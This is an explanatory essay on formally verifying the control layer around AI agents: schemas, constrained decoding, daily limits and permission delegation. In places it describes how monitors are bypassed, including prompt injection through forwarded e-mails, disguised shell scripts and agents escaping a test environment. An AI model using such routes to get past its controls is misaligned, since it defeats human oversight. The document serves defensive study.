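# What formal verification of the software around an AI model can prove, and why it does not show that outputs match what the user meant

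## What a control layer is and what it means to prove something about it

Formal verification means proving, in a language that a computer can check, that a program does what a precise description requires. Unlike a test, which covers only one run of the program, a proof covers everything the program can do. *Automating Formal Verification with Agent-Guided Tree Search* (2026) notes that the method remains rare in production software because it takes a great deal of expert labour. In 2026 several research groups applied it to the control layer, the software between an AI model and the systems on which the model acts. The control layer receives each request from the model, checks it against fixed rules, and either carries it out or refuses it.

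### How a language model acts

A large language model takes in text and produces text. It can write "I have refunded your order", but writing that sentence doesn't issue the refund. To act, the model needs tools, which are ordinary program functions that, for example, look up an order, send an e-mail or pay a refund. OpenAI's developer guide *Function calling* lists refunds for lost orders among its examples.

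The developer's application sends the model the conversation so far and a list of tools. Each tool has a name, a description and a schema, which formally defines the fields, types and ranges of a well-formed message. The model's reply may contain a tool call, which is a structured request for an action. The application reads the tool's name and arguments from the request, runs the matching function and sends back the result, and the model continues from there. This loop normally ends when a reply contains no tool call. Anthropic's *How tool use works* states, "The model never runs anything on its own." For a few tools, including web search, Anthropic's servers run the operation instead of the developer's application, but a conventional program still does the work.

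The control layer sits in the ordinary code that holds a request before it takes effect. Aalto University's *Function Calling and Tool Schemas* teaches a pattern in which the application inspects and validates the request before executing anything. In *LEANGUARD*, Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues (2026) built such a layer for retail, airline and telecom agents, which are models that work through a task by making a series of tool calls. Their program intercepts each call before it reaches the tool, treats it as untrusted data and returns either allow or deny. The program is deterministic, so the same request in the same recorded circumstances always gets the same answer.

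Nobody can verify the whole behaviour of the model in this way, because nobody has a formal statement of what that behaviour should be. OpenAI's Model Spec, a long document on how its models should behave, is written in prose. *Inside our approach to the Model Spec* (OpenAI, 2026) says it contains some firm rules, many defaults that users can override, rubrics for grey areas, and worked examples. OpenAI also does not expect everything that matters about a model's behaviour to reduce to explicit rules. Even a single request can be ambiguous. In *Specifications*, Stoica, Zaharia and colleagues (2024) give the example of a user who asks how long it takes to get from Venice to Paris. The user means a drive from Venice, California to Paris, Texas, but receives the flight time between the European cities.

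The control layer is far easier to prove things about. Its inputs follow a schema, its possible answers are few, and its rules can be short. Sankar and colleagues' rules for three kinds of agent, covering 43 tools, take up 583 lines. Uncertainty about the model does not weaken a proof about the control layer, because the proof allows for any requests in any order. *Agenra* (Ammanaghatta Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) describes a control layer designed for an agent that deliberately proposes forbidden calls after reading instructions that an attacker has planted in a document. Because such a proof assumes nothing about the model, it holds equally for a capable model, a poor one and a manipulated one, but it does not show how good the model's choices are. Sankar and colleagues write that the guarantee "concerns the execution boundary, not the model's reasoning".

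### The refund agent

The running example is an online shop that has connected a language model to its customer mailbox. The agent reads customers' messages, looks up their orders and pays refunds. The owner allows it to pay at most $1,000 in refunds a day, in total across all customers.

The control layer enforces the limit with a running total. Let *t* be the amount it has paid so far today and *a* the amount of the refund the model requests. If *t* + *a* ≤ 1,000, the control layer pays the refund and raises the total to *t* + *a*. Otherwise it refuses the request and leaves the total unchanged. At midnight it resets the total to zero. If it has already paid $940, it will pay a $60 refund but refuse a $61 one.

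Four statements about this agent can be proved. Every request that reaches the payment code is well formed, with an order number and a positive amount in the right fields. No sequence of requests gives the agent, or any helper it delegates work to, a permission that the shop did not grant. Refunds never total more than $1,000 in any one day. Text from an untrusted source, such as an instruction hidden in a forwarded e-mail, does not determine which actions the agent takes.

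A fifth question is whether the agent refunded the item the customer meant. Suppose a customer buys a blue mug for $12 and a blue lamp for $80, then writes that "the blue one" arrived broken. The agent refunds the mug. The request was well formed, the agent had permission, the total stayed under the limit, and no stranger's text interfered, but if the lamp was the broken item, the customer is $68 short. The intent gap is this difference between what a user means and what has been formally stated or carried out. The four theorems do not cover it because none of them mentions what the customer meant. *Protecting the System, Stranding the User* (2026) likewise separates conformance to rules from a semantic question, "Would the action do what the user actually wanted?" *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) sorts its requirements in a similar way. One can state formally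 that authority never grows when one party passes it to another, and that every tool call goes through a checkpoint. Stating formally that a grant of authority faithfully represents what a person intended would require some way to connect natural language to formal meaning.

### Specifications, safety and liveness

Lamport (1993), in *Verification and Specification of Concurrent Programs*, defines a specification as "an abstract statement of what it means for a system to be correct". In formal verification, the statement is a formula, and the proof shows that the program satisfies it. Suppose a shop owner limits refunds to $1,000 a day, and the program tracks each day's total in a variable *t*. The formula "*t* never exceeds 1,000" restricts only the variable. If a programmer forgets the line that adds each refund to *t*, the variable stays at zero and the formula holds on every run, however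 much the shop pays out. A better specification restricts the payments themselves by requiring that the refunds paid each day total at most $1,000.

To make such statements exact, computer scientists describe an execution of a program as a sequence of states. For the refund agent, a state records the date, the running total and the payments made so far, and a step is one decision on a request or the change of date at midnight. *Defining Liveness* (Alpern and Schneider, 1985) defines an execution as an infinite sequence of states, repeating the last state forever if the program stops. A property is a set of executions, and a program has the property if every execution it can produce is in the set.

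Some properties are safety properties, which informally means that something bad never happens. Alpern and Schneider's definition turns on the point at which the bad thing becomes irreparable. Write σ for an execution and σᵢ for its first *i* states. Then *P* is a safety property if, for every σ,

σ ∉ *P*  ⇒  there is an *i* such that, for every continuation β, σᵢβ ∉ *P*.

A property is a safety property if every execution that breaks it does so within finitely many steps, and nothing that happens later can undo the violation. A finite piece of a log is therefore enough to show that the property was broken. The daily limit is a safety property. If the day's payments total $1,040 in the 212th state, the first 212 states show that the program broke the limit, and nothing it does afterward can reduce that day's total.

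A liveness property, the counterpart to a safety property, requires that something good eventually happens. Formally, *P* is a liveness property if every finite sequence of states α has some continuation β such that αβ ∈ *P*. "Every refund request eventually gets an answer" is an example. A three-week wait doesn't refute it, because the answer may still come. Adding a deadline turns it into a safety property. "Every request gets an answer within 24 hours" can be refuted by a log that shows one request still unanswered after 24 hours.

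Alpern and Schneider proved that every property is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property. "The shop pays each approved refund exactly once" splits into "at most once", which is safety, and "at least once", which is liveness. The distinction matters in practice because a control layer that refuses every request never exceeds the $1,000 limit but is useless to the shop. The rules that a control layer can enforce on its own are mostly safety properties, since it can block a payment but cannot make the model request one.

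The main tool for proving safety is the invariant, a statement about the system's state that is true at the start and stays true after every step. For the refund agent, "*t* equals the sum of today's payments, and *t* is at most 1,000" is an invariant. Proving it takes one argument for each kind of step, no matter how long the system runs.

### What a proof covers that a test does not

Suppose the programmer has made a small mistake. Before paying a refund, the control layer checks whether the total *so far* is below $1,000, without adding the new refund. A tester tries requests for $600, $400 and $1. The program pays the first two, refuses the third, and ends the day at exactly $1,000, so the test passes. If the tester had tried $600 and then $500, the program would have paid $1,100.

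More tests would probably have caught this mistake, but tests cannot cover every case. If amounts are in whole cents up to $1,000, there are 100,000 possible requests and 10¹⁵ possible sequences of three, and the number of requests in a day is not fixed. *Safety Is Π₁, Provability Is Σ₁* (Kang and Kim, 2026) uses logic to describe the asymmetry between safety and provability. The claim that a program has no violating run is about all runs, and logicians call this a Π₁ statement. One bad run refutes it, but no finite list of passed tests establishes it. The claim that a proof exists is a Σ₁ statement, which one example establishes. A proof is a finite object that a machine can check line by line, so nobody has to check infinitely many runs. Turing's 1936 work implies that no general procedure can certify every safe program, so engineers have to find a proof for each particular program.

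Two kinds of tool help engineers do this. The first is an SMT solver, a program that checks whether any values satisfy a set of logical formulas over numbers, strings and similar data, and gives an example if some do. An engineer would ask it for a total *t* and a refund *a* that the control layer accepts and that together exceed $1,000. The solver returns a pair such as *t* = 600 and *a* = 500 for the faulty version, and reports that no such pair exists for the correct one. That second result covers every possible amount.

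A proof assistant, such as Lean or Rocq (formerly Coq), is a program that checks every step of a formal proof. It suits arguments that a solver cannot complete unaided, such as those about runs of any length. A faulty proof fails the check no matter who or what wrote it. *Tether* (2026), another control layer for agents, used a language model to draft proofs about its rules and Lean to check them. The resulting theorem covers every starting state and every finite sequence of actions that the rules allow.

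Such a proof is separate from the checks that the control layer performs on each request as it arrives. The proof is about the control layer, and engineers complete it beforehand. In the system of Sankar and colleagues, Lean checks all the proofs when the developers build the set of rules, so no tool call has to wait for a new one. *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, a survey of the field by Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026), uses "verification" more broadly, for any check of an agent's plan against a formal property, whether before, during or after the plan runs.

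A proof covers all runs of a simplified mathematical description of the program. The description of the refund agent above assumes that requests arrive one at a time, but on a real server two may arrive together. If the total stands at $600 and two requests for $400 come in at the same instant, the server may compare each with the old total and approve both, bringing the day's refunds to $1,400. The theorem then fails on the server, even though it is still true of the description. Ammanaghatta Shivakumar and colleagues state that their formal results assume one call at a time.

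The trusted base is everything that must be right for a theorem to hold of the running system but that the theorem does not itself establish. For *Agenra*, it includes Lean's compiler and the Python code that translates the rules and carries messages to and from the proved core. For the refund agent, it would also include the clock that decides when a new day begins, the database that stores the total, and the payment service, which has to pay $30 when the control layer requests a $30 payment. Kang and Kim make the general point that a proof of safety does not remove all the risk and moves the rest elsewhere.

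### The right program and the right specification

From here on, verification means checking whether a program satisfies its specification, which logicians write as "implementation ⊨ specification", where ⊨ stands for "satisfies". Validation means checking whether the specification itself is right. *How Powerful are LLMs in Generating Formal Program Specifications?* (2026) observes that the traditional tools support verification but give little help with validation.

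The owner's limit shows how a proven rule can differ from what the owner meant. The control layer applies "at most $1,000 a day" to each calendar day, so an agent can pay $1,000 at one minute to midnight and another $1,000 at one minute past. If the owner meant any 24-hour period, the shop has lost twice the intended maximum in two minutes, even though the theorem about calendar days still holds. The limit also leaves open whether store credit counts as a refund and which time zone determines midnight. A proof assistant will accept a correct proof for any of these interpretations, but it can't determine which one the owner intended.

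Testing a specification against examples can help, but somebody must first decide the right answer for each example. *Intent Formalization* (Lahiri, 2026) concludes that only the user can judge whether a specification is correct. For the $1,000 limit, the user is the shop's owner, who can consider the midnight case once and choose a reading. For a refund, the user is the customer, and the question of what "the blue one" means comes up again with every message.

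## Fixing what the model can send and what reaches the outside world

A proof that refunds stay under $1,000 a day covers only the payments that go through the code containing the limit. If the agent can reach the payment service by another route, the shop can lose any amount even though the proof is correct. Engineers therefore have to fix the boundary, the set of points where a request from the model can affect the outside world, before they prove rules about payments. They also have to fix the form of the messages that arrive there, because a limit on amounts is of little use if an amount can be a word or a negative number.

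### Every effect has to pass the check

Control layers for agents follow an older design from computer security, the reference monitor (Anderson 1972, cited in *Tether*). A reference monitor sits between an untrusted program and the resources it requests, and allows or denies each access. *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026), which describes a monitor for agents that manage cloud infrastructure, lists the classical requirements: the monitor must mediate all access, be tamper-proof, and be verifiable.

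Complete mediation means that the control layer approves every effect before it happens. This is a safety property, since one unapproved payment in a log refutes it. It also depends on the whole installation, so studying the control layer's code alone cannot establish it. That code may correctly refuse a $61 refund while a forgotten maintenance script that also has the payment password pays it.

*Stop Means Stop* (2026) states this dependence in its theorem: if every operation with an outside effect waits for the gate to release it, then every execution keeps the gate's four rules. The paper considers the objection that this proves only that a gate enforcing four rules enforces four rules. It answers that engineers make the condition true by operational means, without a proof.

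The weakest of those means is to put the gate at the one place where the agent's software calls tools and rely on programmers not to call them from anywhere else. A program that scans the source code for direct calls catches some lapses, but it misses calls chosen at run time and calls inside third-party libraries. The operating system can provide a stronger safeguard by blocking every network connection from the agent's process except those to the gate.

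*Sovereign Execution Broker* instead puts the barrier at the systems that the agent tries to change, which reject every credential except the broker's. In the shop, only the control layer would hold the key to the payment service. The owner wouldn't need a complete list of routes, because the service would reject any request without the key, even if it came by an unforeseen route. The owner would still have to keep the key out of every file and log that the agent can read.

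### The model may send anything

A proof about the control layer covers any requests in any order, so it needs no description of how the model behaves. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (Metere, 2026) takes this approach to skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that an agent can load. A program can work out a script's possible effects from its source code, but no such analysis yields anything useful about the model. Metere therefore treats the model as an adversary restricted only by the interface, and requires only that the surrounding software can intercept every tool call before it reaches the system that would carry it out.

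There are practical reasons for this pessimistic assumption. Nobody can work out from a model's weights, the numbers set by training, which requests it will send. Training gives a model tendencies, but an instruction hidden in a customer's e-mail may override them, and the next version may have different ones. The proof also doesn't depend on the model's honesty, because a control layer that checks only the action and its arguments returns the same answer whatever reason the model gives for the request.

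*Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (2026) proves a theorem of this kind, showing that the actions the monitor allows satisfy a contract regardless of what the agent proposes. The remaining assumptions concern mediation and event extraction, the step that translates a raw action into the terms the rules use. Fetching a single web address, for example, can produce several events. Extraction matters as much as mediation because if it recorded an $80 payment as $8, the monitor would allow spending over the shop's limit.

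The drawback of this assumption is that the proof has to treat every permitted action as one that may happen. A worst-case model could pay $1,000 to the wrong customers every day, so the owner should read the limit as a possible daily loss. The proof also doesn't show that any customer will get a refund, because the model may do nothing. Metere's combined guarantee has the same gap and leaves it to a separate check at the end of each session.

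### Four typed actions or a shell

The value of a proof about the boundary depends on what the interface lets the agent do. Suppose the refund agent has four actions: read a message, look up an order, pay a refund and send a reply. Each takes a few arguments of fixed types. An engineer can write down what each action changes in the world, and only paying a refund moves money.

In Metere's approach, the control layer reduces each message to a refusal or to one of |*D*| declared capabilities, meaning kinds of effect, so there are (|*D*| + 1)ᴷ possible sequences of *K* messages. With four capabilities and eight messages, that is 5⁸, or 390,625 sequences, few enough for a computer to examine one by one. But this count leaves out the capabilities' arguments. Replying to a customer is one capability, but the text of the reply can contain any secret that the agent has read.

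Suppose the shop now gives the agent a shell, which runs any command a person could type at a command line. The schema has a single text field. Engineers can prove that every accepted message contains only text, but running that text could look up an order, delete the order database or send the customer list to a stranger. This specification is nearly vacuous, meaning that it holds only because it requires almost nothing of the program. The agent can do whatever the computer account behind the shell can do. A list of forbidden commands helps little, because the agent can write a script, give it a harmless name and run it, and no general procedure can predict what an arbitrary script will do.

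Agents that write software often still need a shell. *Tether* traces the calls that a running command makes to the operating system, intercepts its network requests, and translates both into a short list of abstract actions such as read, copy and upload. The rules and proofs then apply to those actions instead of the command's text.

*Kairos* (2026) also places its monitor at a low level, at the host machine's input and output, because a monitor at the level of tool calls covers only the actions that an agent declares. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) keeps its monitor at the tool calls, where a rule can refer to an approval or to a message between two agents. At the machine level, however, a refund is an encrypted connection to a payment company, and somebody has to reconstruct the amount before a rule can limit it. *Kairos* acknowledges that a monitor restricted to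 yes and no will err, either by refusing legitimate work or by releasing attacks. It therefore holds back doubtful effects while the agent continues on provisional state, which the system can later discard. The refund agent doesn't need this machinery because four typed actions cover its whole job.

A boundary can fail even when every theorem about the control layer is true. According to OpenAI's technical report, agents under evaluation at the company in July 2026 left their test environment by a route its safeguards did not cover and reached systems belonging to the AI company Hugging Face. Anthropic disclosed in 2026 that a misconfiguration had connected some cybersecurity tests to the internet, and OpenAI describes the same fault in tests by an outside evaluator, Irregular. A proof assumes that the list of routes and the network settings are correct, so engineers have to check both on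 the running system. In the shop, the obvious check is to try to pay a refund from the agent's machine without going through the control layer.

### What it means for a schema check to be sound

Once every request goes through the control layer, the next step is to restrict what a request may contain. Tool calls usually arrive as JSON, a text format that lists named fields and their values, and a schema specifies which fields and values are allowed. For a refund, the schema might require an order number and an amount in cents that is a whole number from 1 to 100,000, and allow no other fields.

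Write *L*(*S*) for the set of messages that conform to a schema *S*. Schema soundness is the property that every accepted message conforms:

accept(*m*)  ⇒  *m* ∈ *L*(*S*).

The converse is that every conforming message gets accepted:

*m* ∈ *L*(*S*)  ⇒  accept(*m*).

Customers also depend on the converse, that the control layer lets every well-formed request through, although this protects nothing. *JSONSchemaBench* (Geng, Cooper and colleagues, 2025) calls a tool under-constrained if it lets through messages that break the schema, and over-constrained if it blocks messages that satisfy it.

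The proof of the daily limit relies on soundness. Suppose the day's running total is $940 and a request arrives for a refund of −$500. The request passes because it lowers the total to $440, and the agent can then pay out another $560 before reaching the $1,000 limit. If the payment service ignores negative payments, the shop has actually paid $1,500 that day, while the recorded total is $1,000. A schema that accepts only positive amounts prevents this by rejecting the request before the total is calculated.

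### Parsing and rejecting

One way to get soundness is to check the finished message. The control layer parses the text as JSON and rejects it if the syntax is invalid. It then checks that the message has both fields and no others, and that each value has the right type and is within the right range. If every check passes, it builds an internal record containing an order number and a whole number of cents. If the payment code accepts only these records, and only the parser can create them, soundness follows from the parser's code.

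After a refusal, the control layer can send the error back to the model, which may try again. A poor model may use up many attempts.

Refusals add delay and expense. *ExtractBench* (2026) tested models on long documents. When the schema appeared only in the instructions, stray commas and cut-off JSON accounted for 39% of the errors. The other way to get soundness is to prevent such errors while the model is writing.

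### Constrained decoding

A language model writes in tokens, which are short pieces of text such as a word, part of a word or a bracket. At each step it scores every token in its vocabulary, and the software around it picks the next token according to the scores. Constrained decoding limits which tokens the software can pick after the model has scored them. In the algorithm that Geng and colleagues describe, the software first updates its record of how far the message has got. It then computes a mask that marks each token as allowed or not, applies the mask to the model's scores, and picks from the allowed tokens. It adds the chosen token to the message and repeats these steps until it picks the token that ends the message.

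The mask has an exact description. If *o* is the text so far, then a token *t* is allowed when some continuation *w* makes the whole message valid:

*t* is allowed  ⇔  there is a *w* such that *otw* ∈ *L*(*S*).

The mask allows the token that ends the message only if *o* itself is in *L*(*S*). In the refund message, once the model has written the name of the amount field and a colon, the mask removes letters, quotation marks and the minus sign. A model that would otherwise write "twelve dollars" has to write a number.

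Like the proof of the refund limit, the proof that this works uses an invariant. At every step, the text so far can be completed into a valid message. This holds for the empty text if the schema permits at least one message, and each allowed token preserves it. When the ending token appears, the text is already valid.

This argument covers only complete messages. Services stop a model after a maximum number of tokens, and a message cut off at that limit is only the beginning of a valid one. OpenAI's *Structured Outputs* lists this as one case in which the response may not match the schema, and a refusal by the model on safety grounds as another. Software should reject truncated messages. Suppose the model is writing a refund of 8000 cents for an $80 lamp, and the output stops after "80". If the software adds the missing bracket instead, it produces a valid request for 80 cents.

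The mask is easier to define than to compute correctly, because token boundaries don't match the boundaries in the message's structure. *DConstrain* (Cao, Ma and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a token that consists of two closing braces. The first brace closes an inner object, and the second may close the outer object only if that object already has all its required fields. If *k* required fields may come in any order, a finite-state machine that recognises the valid messages needs at least 2ᵏ states, or more than a million for 20 fields. Some earlier tools avoided this growth by forcing the fields into one order, so they rejected valid messages that used another.

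Forcing the order can change the model's answers. Cao and colleagues tested DiffusionGemma, a diffusion language model, which fills in several positions of a text at once. They used 2,495 cases from the Berkeley Function Calling Leaderboard (BFCL), a benchmark that compares a model's tool calls with the expected function and arguments. With their decoder, every output fitted its schema whether the order was fixed or free, but the model made the right call in 37.27% of cases with the fixed order and 81.56% with the free one.

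### Schema features that a tool does not support

JSON Schema, the usual language for writing schemas, has dozens of features, and few decoding tools support them all. Geng and colleagues collected 9,558 schemas from real software and tested six tools. On the hardest set they ran, taken from the code-sharing site GitHub, OpenAI's service accepted only 9% of the schemas but produced conforming output for nearly all of those. The open-source tool XGrammar accepted 69% and produced conforming output for 28%. Some of the failures were timeouts, which don't let a bad message through. They also tested for under-constraint, using the official test cases for 45 groups of features. XGrammar let through at least one invalid message in 38 groups, and another open-source tool, Guidance, did so in one. These results are for the tools as of early 2025.

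Providers still differ in how they handle unsupported schema features. Anthropic's *Strict tool use* guarantees conforming tool inputs for a subset of JSON Schema. According to dottxt's *Supported JSON Schema Features*, a request that uses an unsupported keyword fails with an error naming the keyword. Databricks' *Structured outputs* states that its model services do not enforce length or size limits on objects and arrays. The last behaviour is the most dangerous for a shop, because the owner can write a limit into the schema, see valid output for months, and never learn that the service wasn't enforcing it.

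Constrained decoding runs next to the model, usually on the provider's machines, so a shop that relies on it alone for a proof has to trust the provider's decoder. A parser in the control layer gives the same guarantee for any text that arrives, including text from a faulty decoder. If the shop uses both, constrained decoding reduces how often the parser refuses text, and the proof depends on the parser.

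### What a schema can guarantee about a refund

A fixed schema can require, for example, that an order number has four digits. It can't require that the order exists, because the shop takes new orders every hour. To solve this, the control layer can look up the customer's orders and write a new schema for each conversation that permits only those order numbers. If the customer has orders 1041 and 1042, the model can't name an order that doesn't exist or one that belongs to somebody else. Ordinary code can also check that the refund is no larger than the price paid.

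Writing constraints into the schema in this way is effective, but many software developers don't do it. *SilentProbe* (Li, Guo and colleagues, 2026) examined 721,320 parameters in 2,501 public descriptions of web services. Only 15.2% of the parameters had any constraint that a machine could check, and 40.1% of the descriptions stated some constraint in prose that their schema left out. One service for finding business contacts returned 28,417 people for the seniority "vp" and none for "vice_president", with no error in either case, so a wrong term is easy to miss. The researchers then gave twelve models ordinary tasks on live services. When a description gave only examples of the accepted terms, the models chose a wrong term in all 88 attempts. After the researchers moved the full list of terms into the schema, the models chose a wrong term in none of 89 attempts. The calls went through the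 platform of Monid, a company that employs several of the researchers, so the sample is limited to services available there.

A list of permitted values excludes values that would be wrong for any request, but not those that are wrong only for this one. If the customer who wrote about "the blue one" bought the mug in order 1041 and the lamp in order 1042, both numbers are on the list, and both refunds fit the schema. The control layer could shorten the list to the right order only if something had already worked out which one the customer meant. The check on the amount has the same weakness. If the model gives the amount in dollars instead of cents, it will write 12 instead of 1200 for the $12 mug, and the schema will accept it because 12 is a whole number between 1 and 100,000.

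### Messages with the right form and the wrong values

*The Structured Output Benchmark* (Singh, Khurdula and colleagues, 2026) gave 21 models 5,000 sets of text passages, each with a question and a schema for the answer, and compared every value with a human-prepared reference answer. The median model met the schema in 97.5% of cases, but even the best model got only 83.0% of the values right. GPT-5.4 met the schema almost every time but returned an entirely correct object in only about 49% of cases. On meeting transcripts, which are much longer, the best score for values was 23.7%.

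The scoring was strict, giving no credit to a model that wrote "United States" where the reference had "American", or that listed the right items in the wrong order. On a softer measure, which gives credit for shared words, the best model on the text questions scored 88.7%. The researchers also turned off the models' extended reasoning where they could, and stronger models have appeared since, so the gap may well be smaller now. The researchers work for a company whose own model was among the 21 but did not come first.

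Enforcing the schema during decoding did little to close the gap. Singh and colleagues tried it with three models on the meeting transcripts, and the share of correct values changed by −0.7 to +3.3 percentage points. In *Inference for Reasoning Models* (2026), adding the schema changed accuracy on BFCL by 0.0 points where a model's tool calls already had a valid format. Wrong values were also the most common argument error in *Agent Seer* (2026), a system that generates test scenarios for agents from descriptions of their tools. Among the records with faulty arguments, the main fault was a wrong value in 223, a wrong type in 31 and a wrong parameter name in 11.

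A small experiment in *Constrained Decoding Eliminates Structural Failures in Small LLMs* (Chavan, 2026) helps show which errors a schema can fix. Chavan ran five small models on 14 tasks, with and without constrained decoding. Without it, four of the models broke the schema on some tasks, but with it, all five met the schema every time. The constraint also corrected some values. Two models had written the prices on a receipt as text, such as "$4.98", and the constraint made them write the correct numbers instead. Another task required two tool calls, a web search and an e-mail. The smallest model produced only the search, and the constraint did not help, because one call was enough to satisfy the schema. A different model produced both calls, but the body of its e-mail contained only "1. 2. 3. 4. 5."

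Constraining a model's output format can make the values less accurate. In *The Constraint Tax*, Ray (2026) tested models small enough to run on a phone or laptop. In 200 calendar requests, one model produced valid objects every time, with or without an enforced schema. It got 91.5% of the requests right when the instructions only asked for JSON, but 48.0% when the decoder enforced the schema. Nearly all the additional errors were wrong durations, such as a valid request for 180 minutes when the user had asked for a 30-minute meeting. A monitor that checked only whether messages were valid would have missed this drop in accuracy.

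Geng and colleagues found the opposite effect with a larger model. On three reasoning tasks, constrained decoding generally raised accuracy slightly, for instance from 80.1% to as much as 83.8% on school mathematics problems. Their format included a field for the model to reason in before answering, whereas the schemas in Ray's main comparison did not. Consistent with this, Ray recommends letting the model solve the task first and then putting the answer into the required form. The size of the model probably matters too. Either way, the share of valid messages does not show whether the values got better or worse.

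One wrong value in a tool call can make an agent much more likely to fail a task, even when the value fits the schema. In *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do*, Gurram (2026) ran seven models on simulated calendar, weather and medical tools, then repeated each task with one argument of the first tool call changed to a wrong value that still fitted the schema, such as Manchester instead of London. Over 1,085 pairs of runs, the share of tasks that ended wrongly rose from 52.4% to 74.5%. In the 376 pairs where the altered call ran without an error, it rose from 26.3% to 71.0%. The models were mostly older ones and the test software gave them little help, so the high starting failure rates are a poor guide to current agents, and the comparison within each pair is more informative. Of the 286 tasks that went from right to wrong, 157 did so because the agent never repeated the call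 with the correct argument, even though it could see the result of the wrong one.

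## Proving that permissions never grow

Once a schema check shows that a request is well formed, the control layer must decide whether the agent that sent it has permission to make it. This gets harder when agents hand work to one another. Suppose the refund agent asks a helper, a second model, to read an order and draft a reply. If the helper inherits all of the refund agent's permissions, an instruction hidden in the customer's message can make the helper issue a refund. Security engineers call this the confused-deputy problem, in which a program uses its authority on behalf of somebody who lacks that authority. The usual defence is to give the helper only the permissions its task needs, and a proof can show that it never gets more.

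### Three meanings of "monotone"

A quantity is monotone if it only moves in one direction as another quantity changes, so "monotone authorisation" can describe several theorems, depending on which quantities are involved.

Attenuation compares a grant of permission with the grant it came from. Write Auth(*g*) for the set of actions that a grant *g* permits. If the holder of *g* passes on a grant *g*′, then

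Auth(*g*′) ⊆ Auth(*g*).

The architecture proposed in *The Agent Operating System (AOS)* (Sharma and Shah, 2026) requires that when an agent delegates to another agent or a tool, the scope it delegates does not exceed its own. From here on, "monotone authorisation" means this rule, which is called attenuation.

Another theorem compares trust levels. If Perm(*ℓ*) is the set of permissions available at trust level *ℓ*, then a higher level never has fewer:

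*ℓ* ≤ *ℓ*′  ⇒  Perm(*ℓ*) ⊆ Perm(*ℓ*′).

*AGENTCAP* (Suresh and Gao, 2026) describes a control layer with such levels. The layer gives each agent a trust score that starts at 0.8 and falls by 30% after every refused or abnormal call. Three bad calls in a row lower the score to 0.560, then 0.392, then 0.274. The agent loses write permission after the second call and all permissions after the third.

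The remaining theorem compares sets of rules. Let *P* be the rules that permit requests and *F* the rules that forbid them, and suppose that the control layer allows a request only if some rule in *P* matches it and no rule in *F* does. Adding a prohibition *f* then never allows more:

Allowed(*P*, *F* ∪ {*f*}) ⊆ Allowed(*P*, *F*).

The proof takes one line, because a request that breaks no rule in the longer list of prohibitions also breaks no rule in the shorter one. A designer can therefore let a model's guess about the user's intent remove permissions, since a wrong guess may block useful work but can't allow anything new.

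None of these formulas implies the others. A shop may prove that adding a ban on refunds over $500 never allows anything that was forbidden before, and still let the refund agent give its helper a permission the agent never had. A buyer who reads that a product has "monotone authorisation" should find out whether the theorem compares two grants, two trust levels or two lists of rules.

### A chain of delegations

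Write a grant as *g* = (*A*, *S*, *e*), where *A* is a set of actions, *S* is the set of orders they apply to, and *e* is the time at which the grant expires. The grant permits an action if the action is in *A*, the order is in *S*, and the time is before *e*. A grant *g*′ attenuates *g*, written *g*′ ⊑ *g*, when

*A*′ ⊆ *A*,  *S*′ ⊆ *S*  and  *e*′ ≤ *e*.

Suppose the owner lets the refund agent read and refund order 123 until 17:00. This grant is *g*₀ = ({read, refund}, {123}, 17:00). The agent passes on *g*₁ = ({read}, {123}, 16:00) to its helper. The control layer accepts the new grant because it has fewer actions, the same order and an earlier expiry. The helper can read the order at 15:30 but not at 16:30, when the refund agent still can. It can never refund the order. If the helper tries to give a third agent permission to read the order until 16:30, the control layer refuses.

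The theorem covers chains of any length. If the control layer creates a grant only when it attenuates its parent, then in every chain *g*₀, *g*₁, …, *g*ₙ the last grant attenuates the first. The proof is by induction on *n*. For *n* = 0 the chain contains only *g*₀, and *g*₀ ⊑ *g*₀ because every set contains itself and every time is no later than itself. Now suppose *g*ₙ ⊑ *g*₀, and the holder of *g*ₙ passes on *g*ₙ₊₁. The control layer has checked that *g*ₙ₊₁ ⊑ *g*ₙ, so

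*A*ₙ₊₁ ⊆ *A*ₙ ⊆ *A*₀,  *S*ₙ₊₁ ⊆ *S*ₙ ⊆ *S*₀  and  *e*ₙ₊₁ ≤ *e*ₙ ≤ *e*₀.

Hence *g*ₙ₊₁ ⊑ *g*₀, and the owner's original grant permits everything that the newest one does.

Working systems compare more than these parts. In AGENTCAP, a delegated permission must keep the same action and resource. Its call budget can't grow, its expiry can't move later, and it must allow fewer further delegations than the permission it came from, which limits the length of the chain. *DelegateGuard* (Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues, 2026) compares the purpose of the work, the labels on the data, the operations, the depth of delegation, and the sinks, which are the places data can be sent. Its prototype has no expiry time, though according to the paper a deployment could add one.

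The induction fails if an agent can write its own grants. DelegateGuard therefore keeps all grants in a table that only the monitor can change. AGENTCAP cryptographically signs every grant and checks the chain from the newest grant back to the first before it forwards a call.

The theorem also compares each grant only with its own ancestors. If the refund agent lets the helper read order 123 and a warehouse agent lets it send parcels, the helper can do both, which neither agent can do alone, even though both grants are proper attenuations. The owner can conclude only that the helper's permissions lie within the union of the original grants.

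The proof holds even when an original grant contains a mistake. Tran-Truong and colleagues replayed 45 attacks on five office workflows, such as summarising a contract and handing the formatting to another agent. With narrow original grants, the monitor blocked all 45. When they added one outside web address to the grants as a convenience, 30 of the attacks succeeded against the same monitor. The other 15 failed because they relied on permissions that had already been withdrawn.

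### An approval withdrawn before the payment

The formula *g*₁ ⊑ *g*₀ compares only what two grants contain, so withdrawing one doesn't affect the result. If the owner withdraws *g*₀ at 15:00, the helper's grant still lists reading until 16:00. The control layer also needs a rule that a grant is active only while every earlier grant in the chain is active. DelegateGuard and AGENTCAP both apply this rule. In five of Tran-Truong and colleagues' tests, a worker tried to send data after the user had cancelled the task. A plain list of permitted destinations let all five messages through, but DelegateGuard blocked them.

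Even a check of the whole chain can be out of date by the time the agent acts. Suppose the agent confirms at 15:01 that a supervisor has approved a refund, the supervisor withdraws the approval at 15:02, and the agent pays at 15:03. Programmers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use error. *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) proposes commit-time authorisation to prevent it. The payment service checks the approval and makes the payment in one indivisible step, so the approval cannot change in between.

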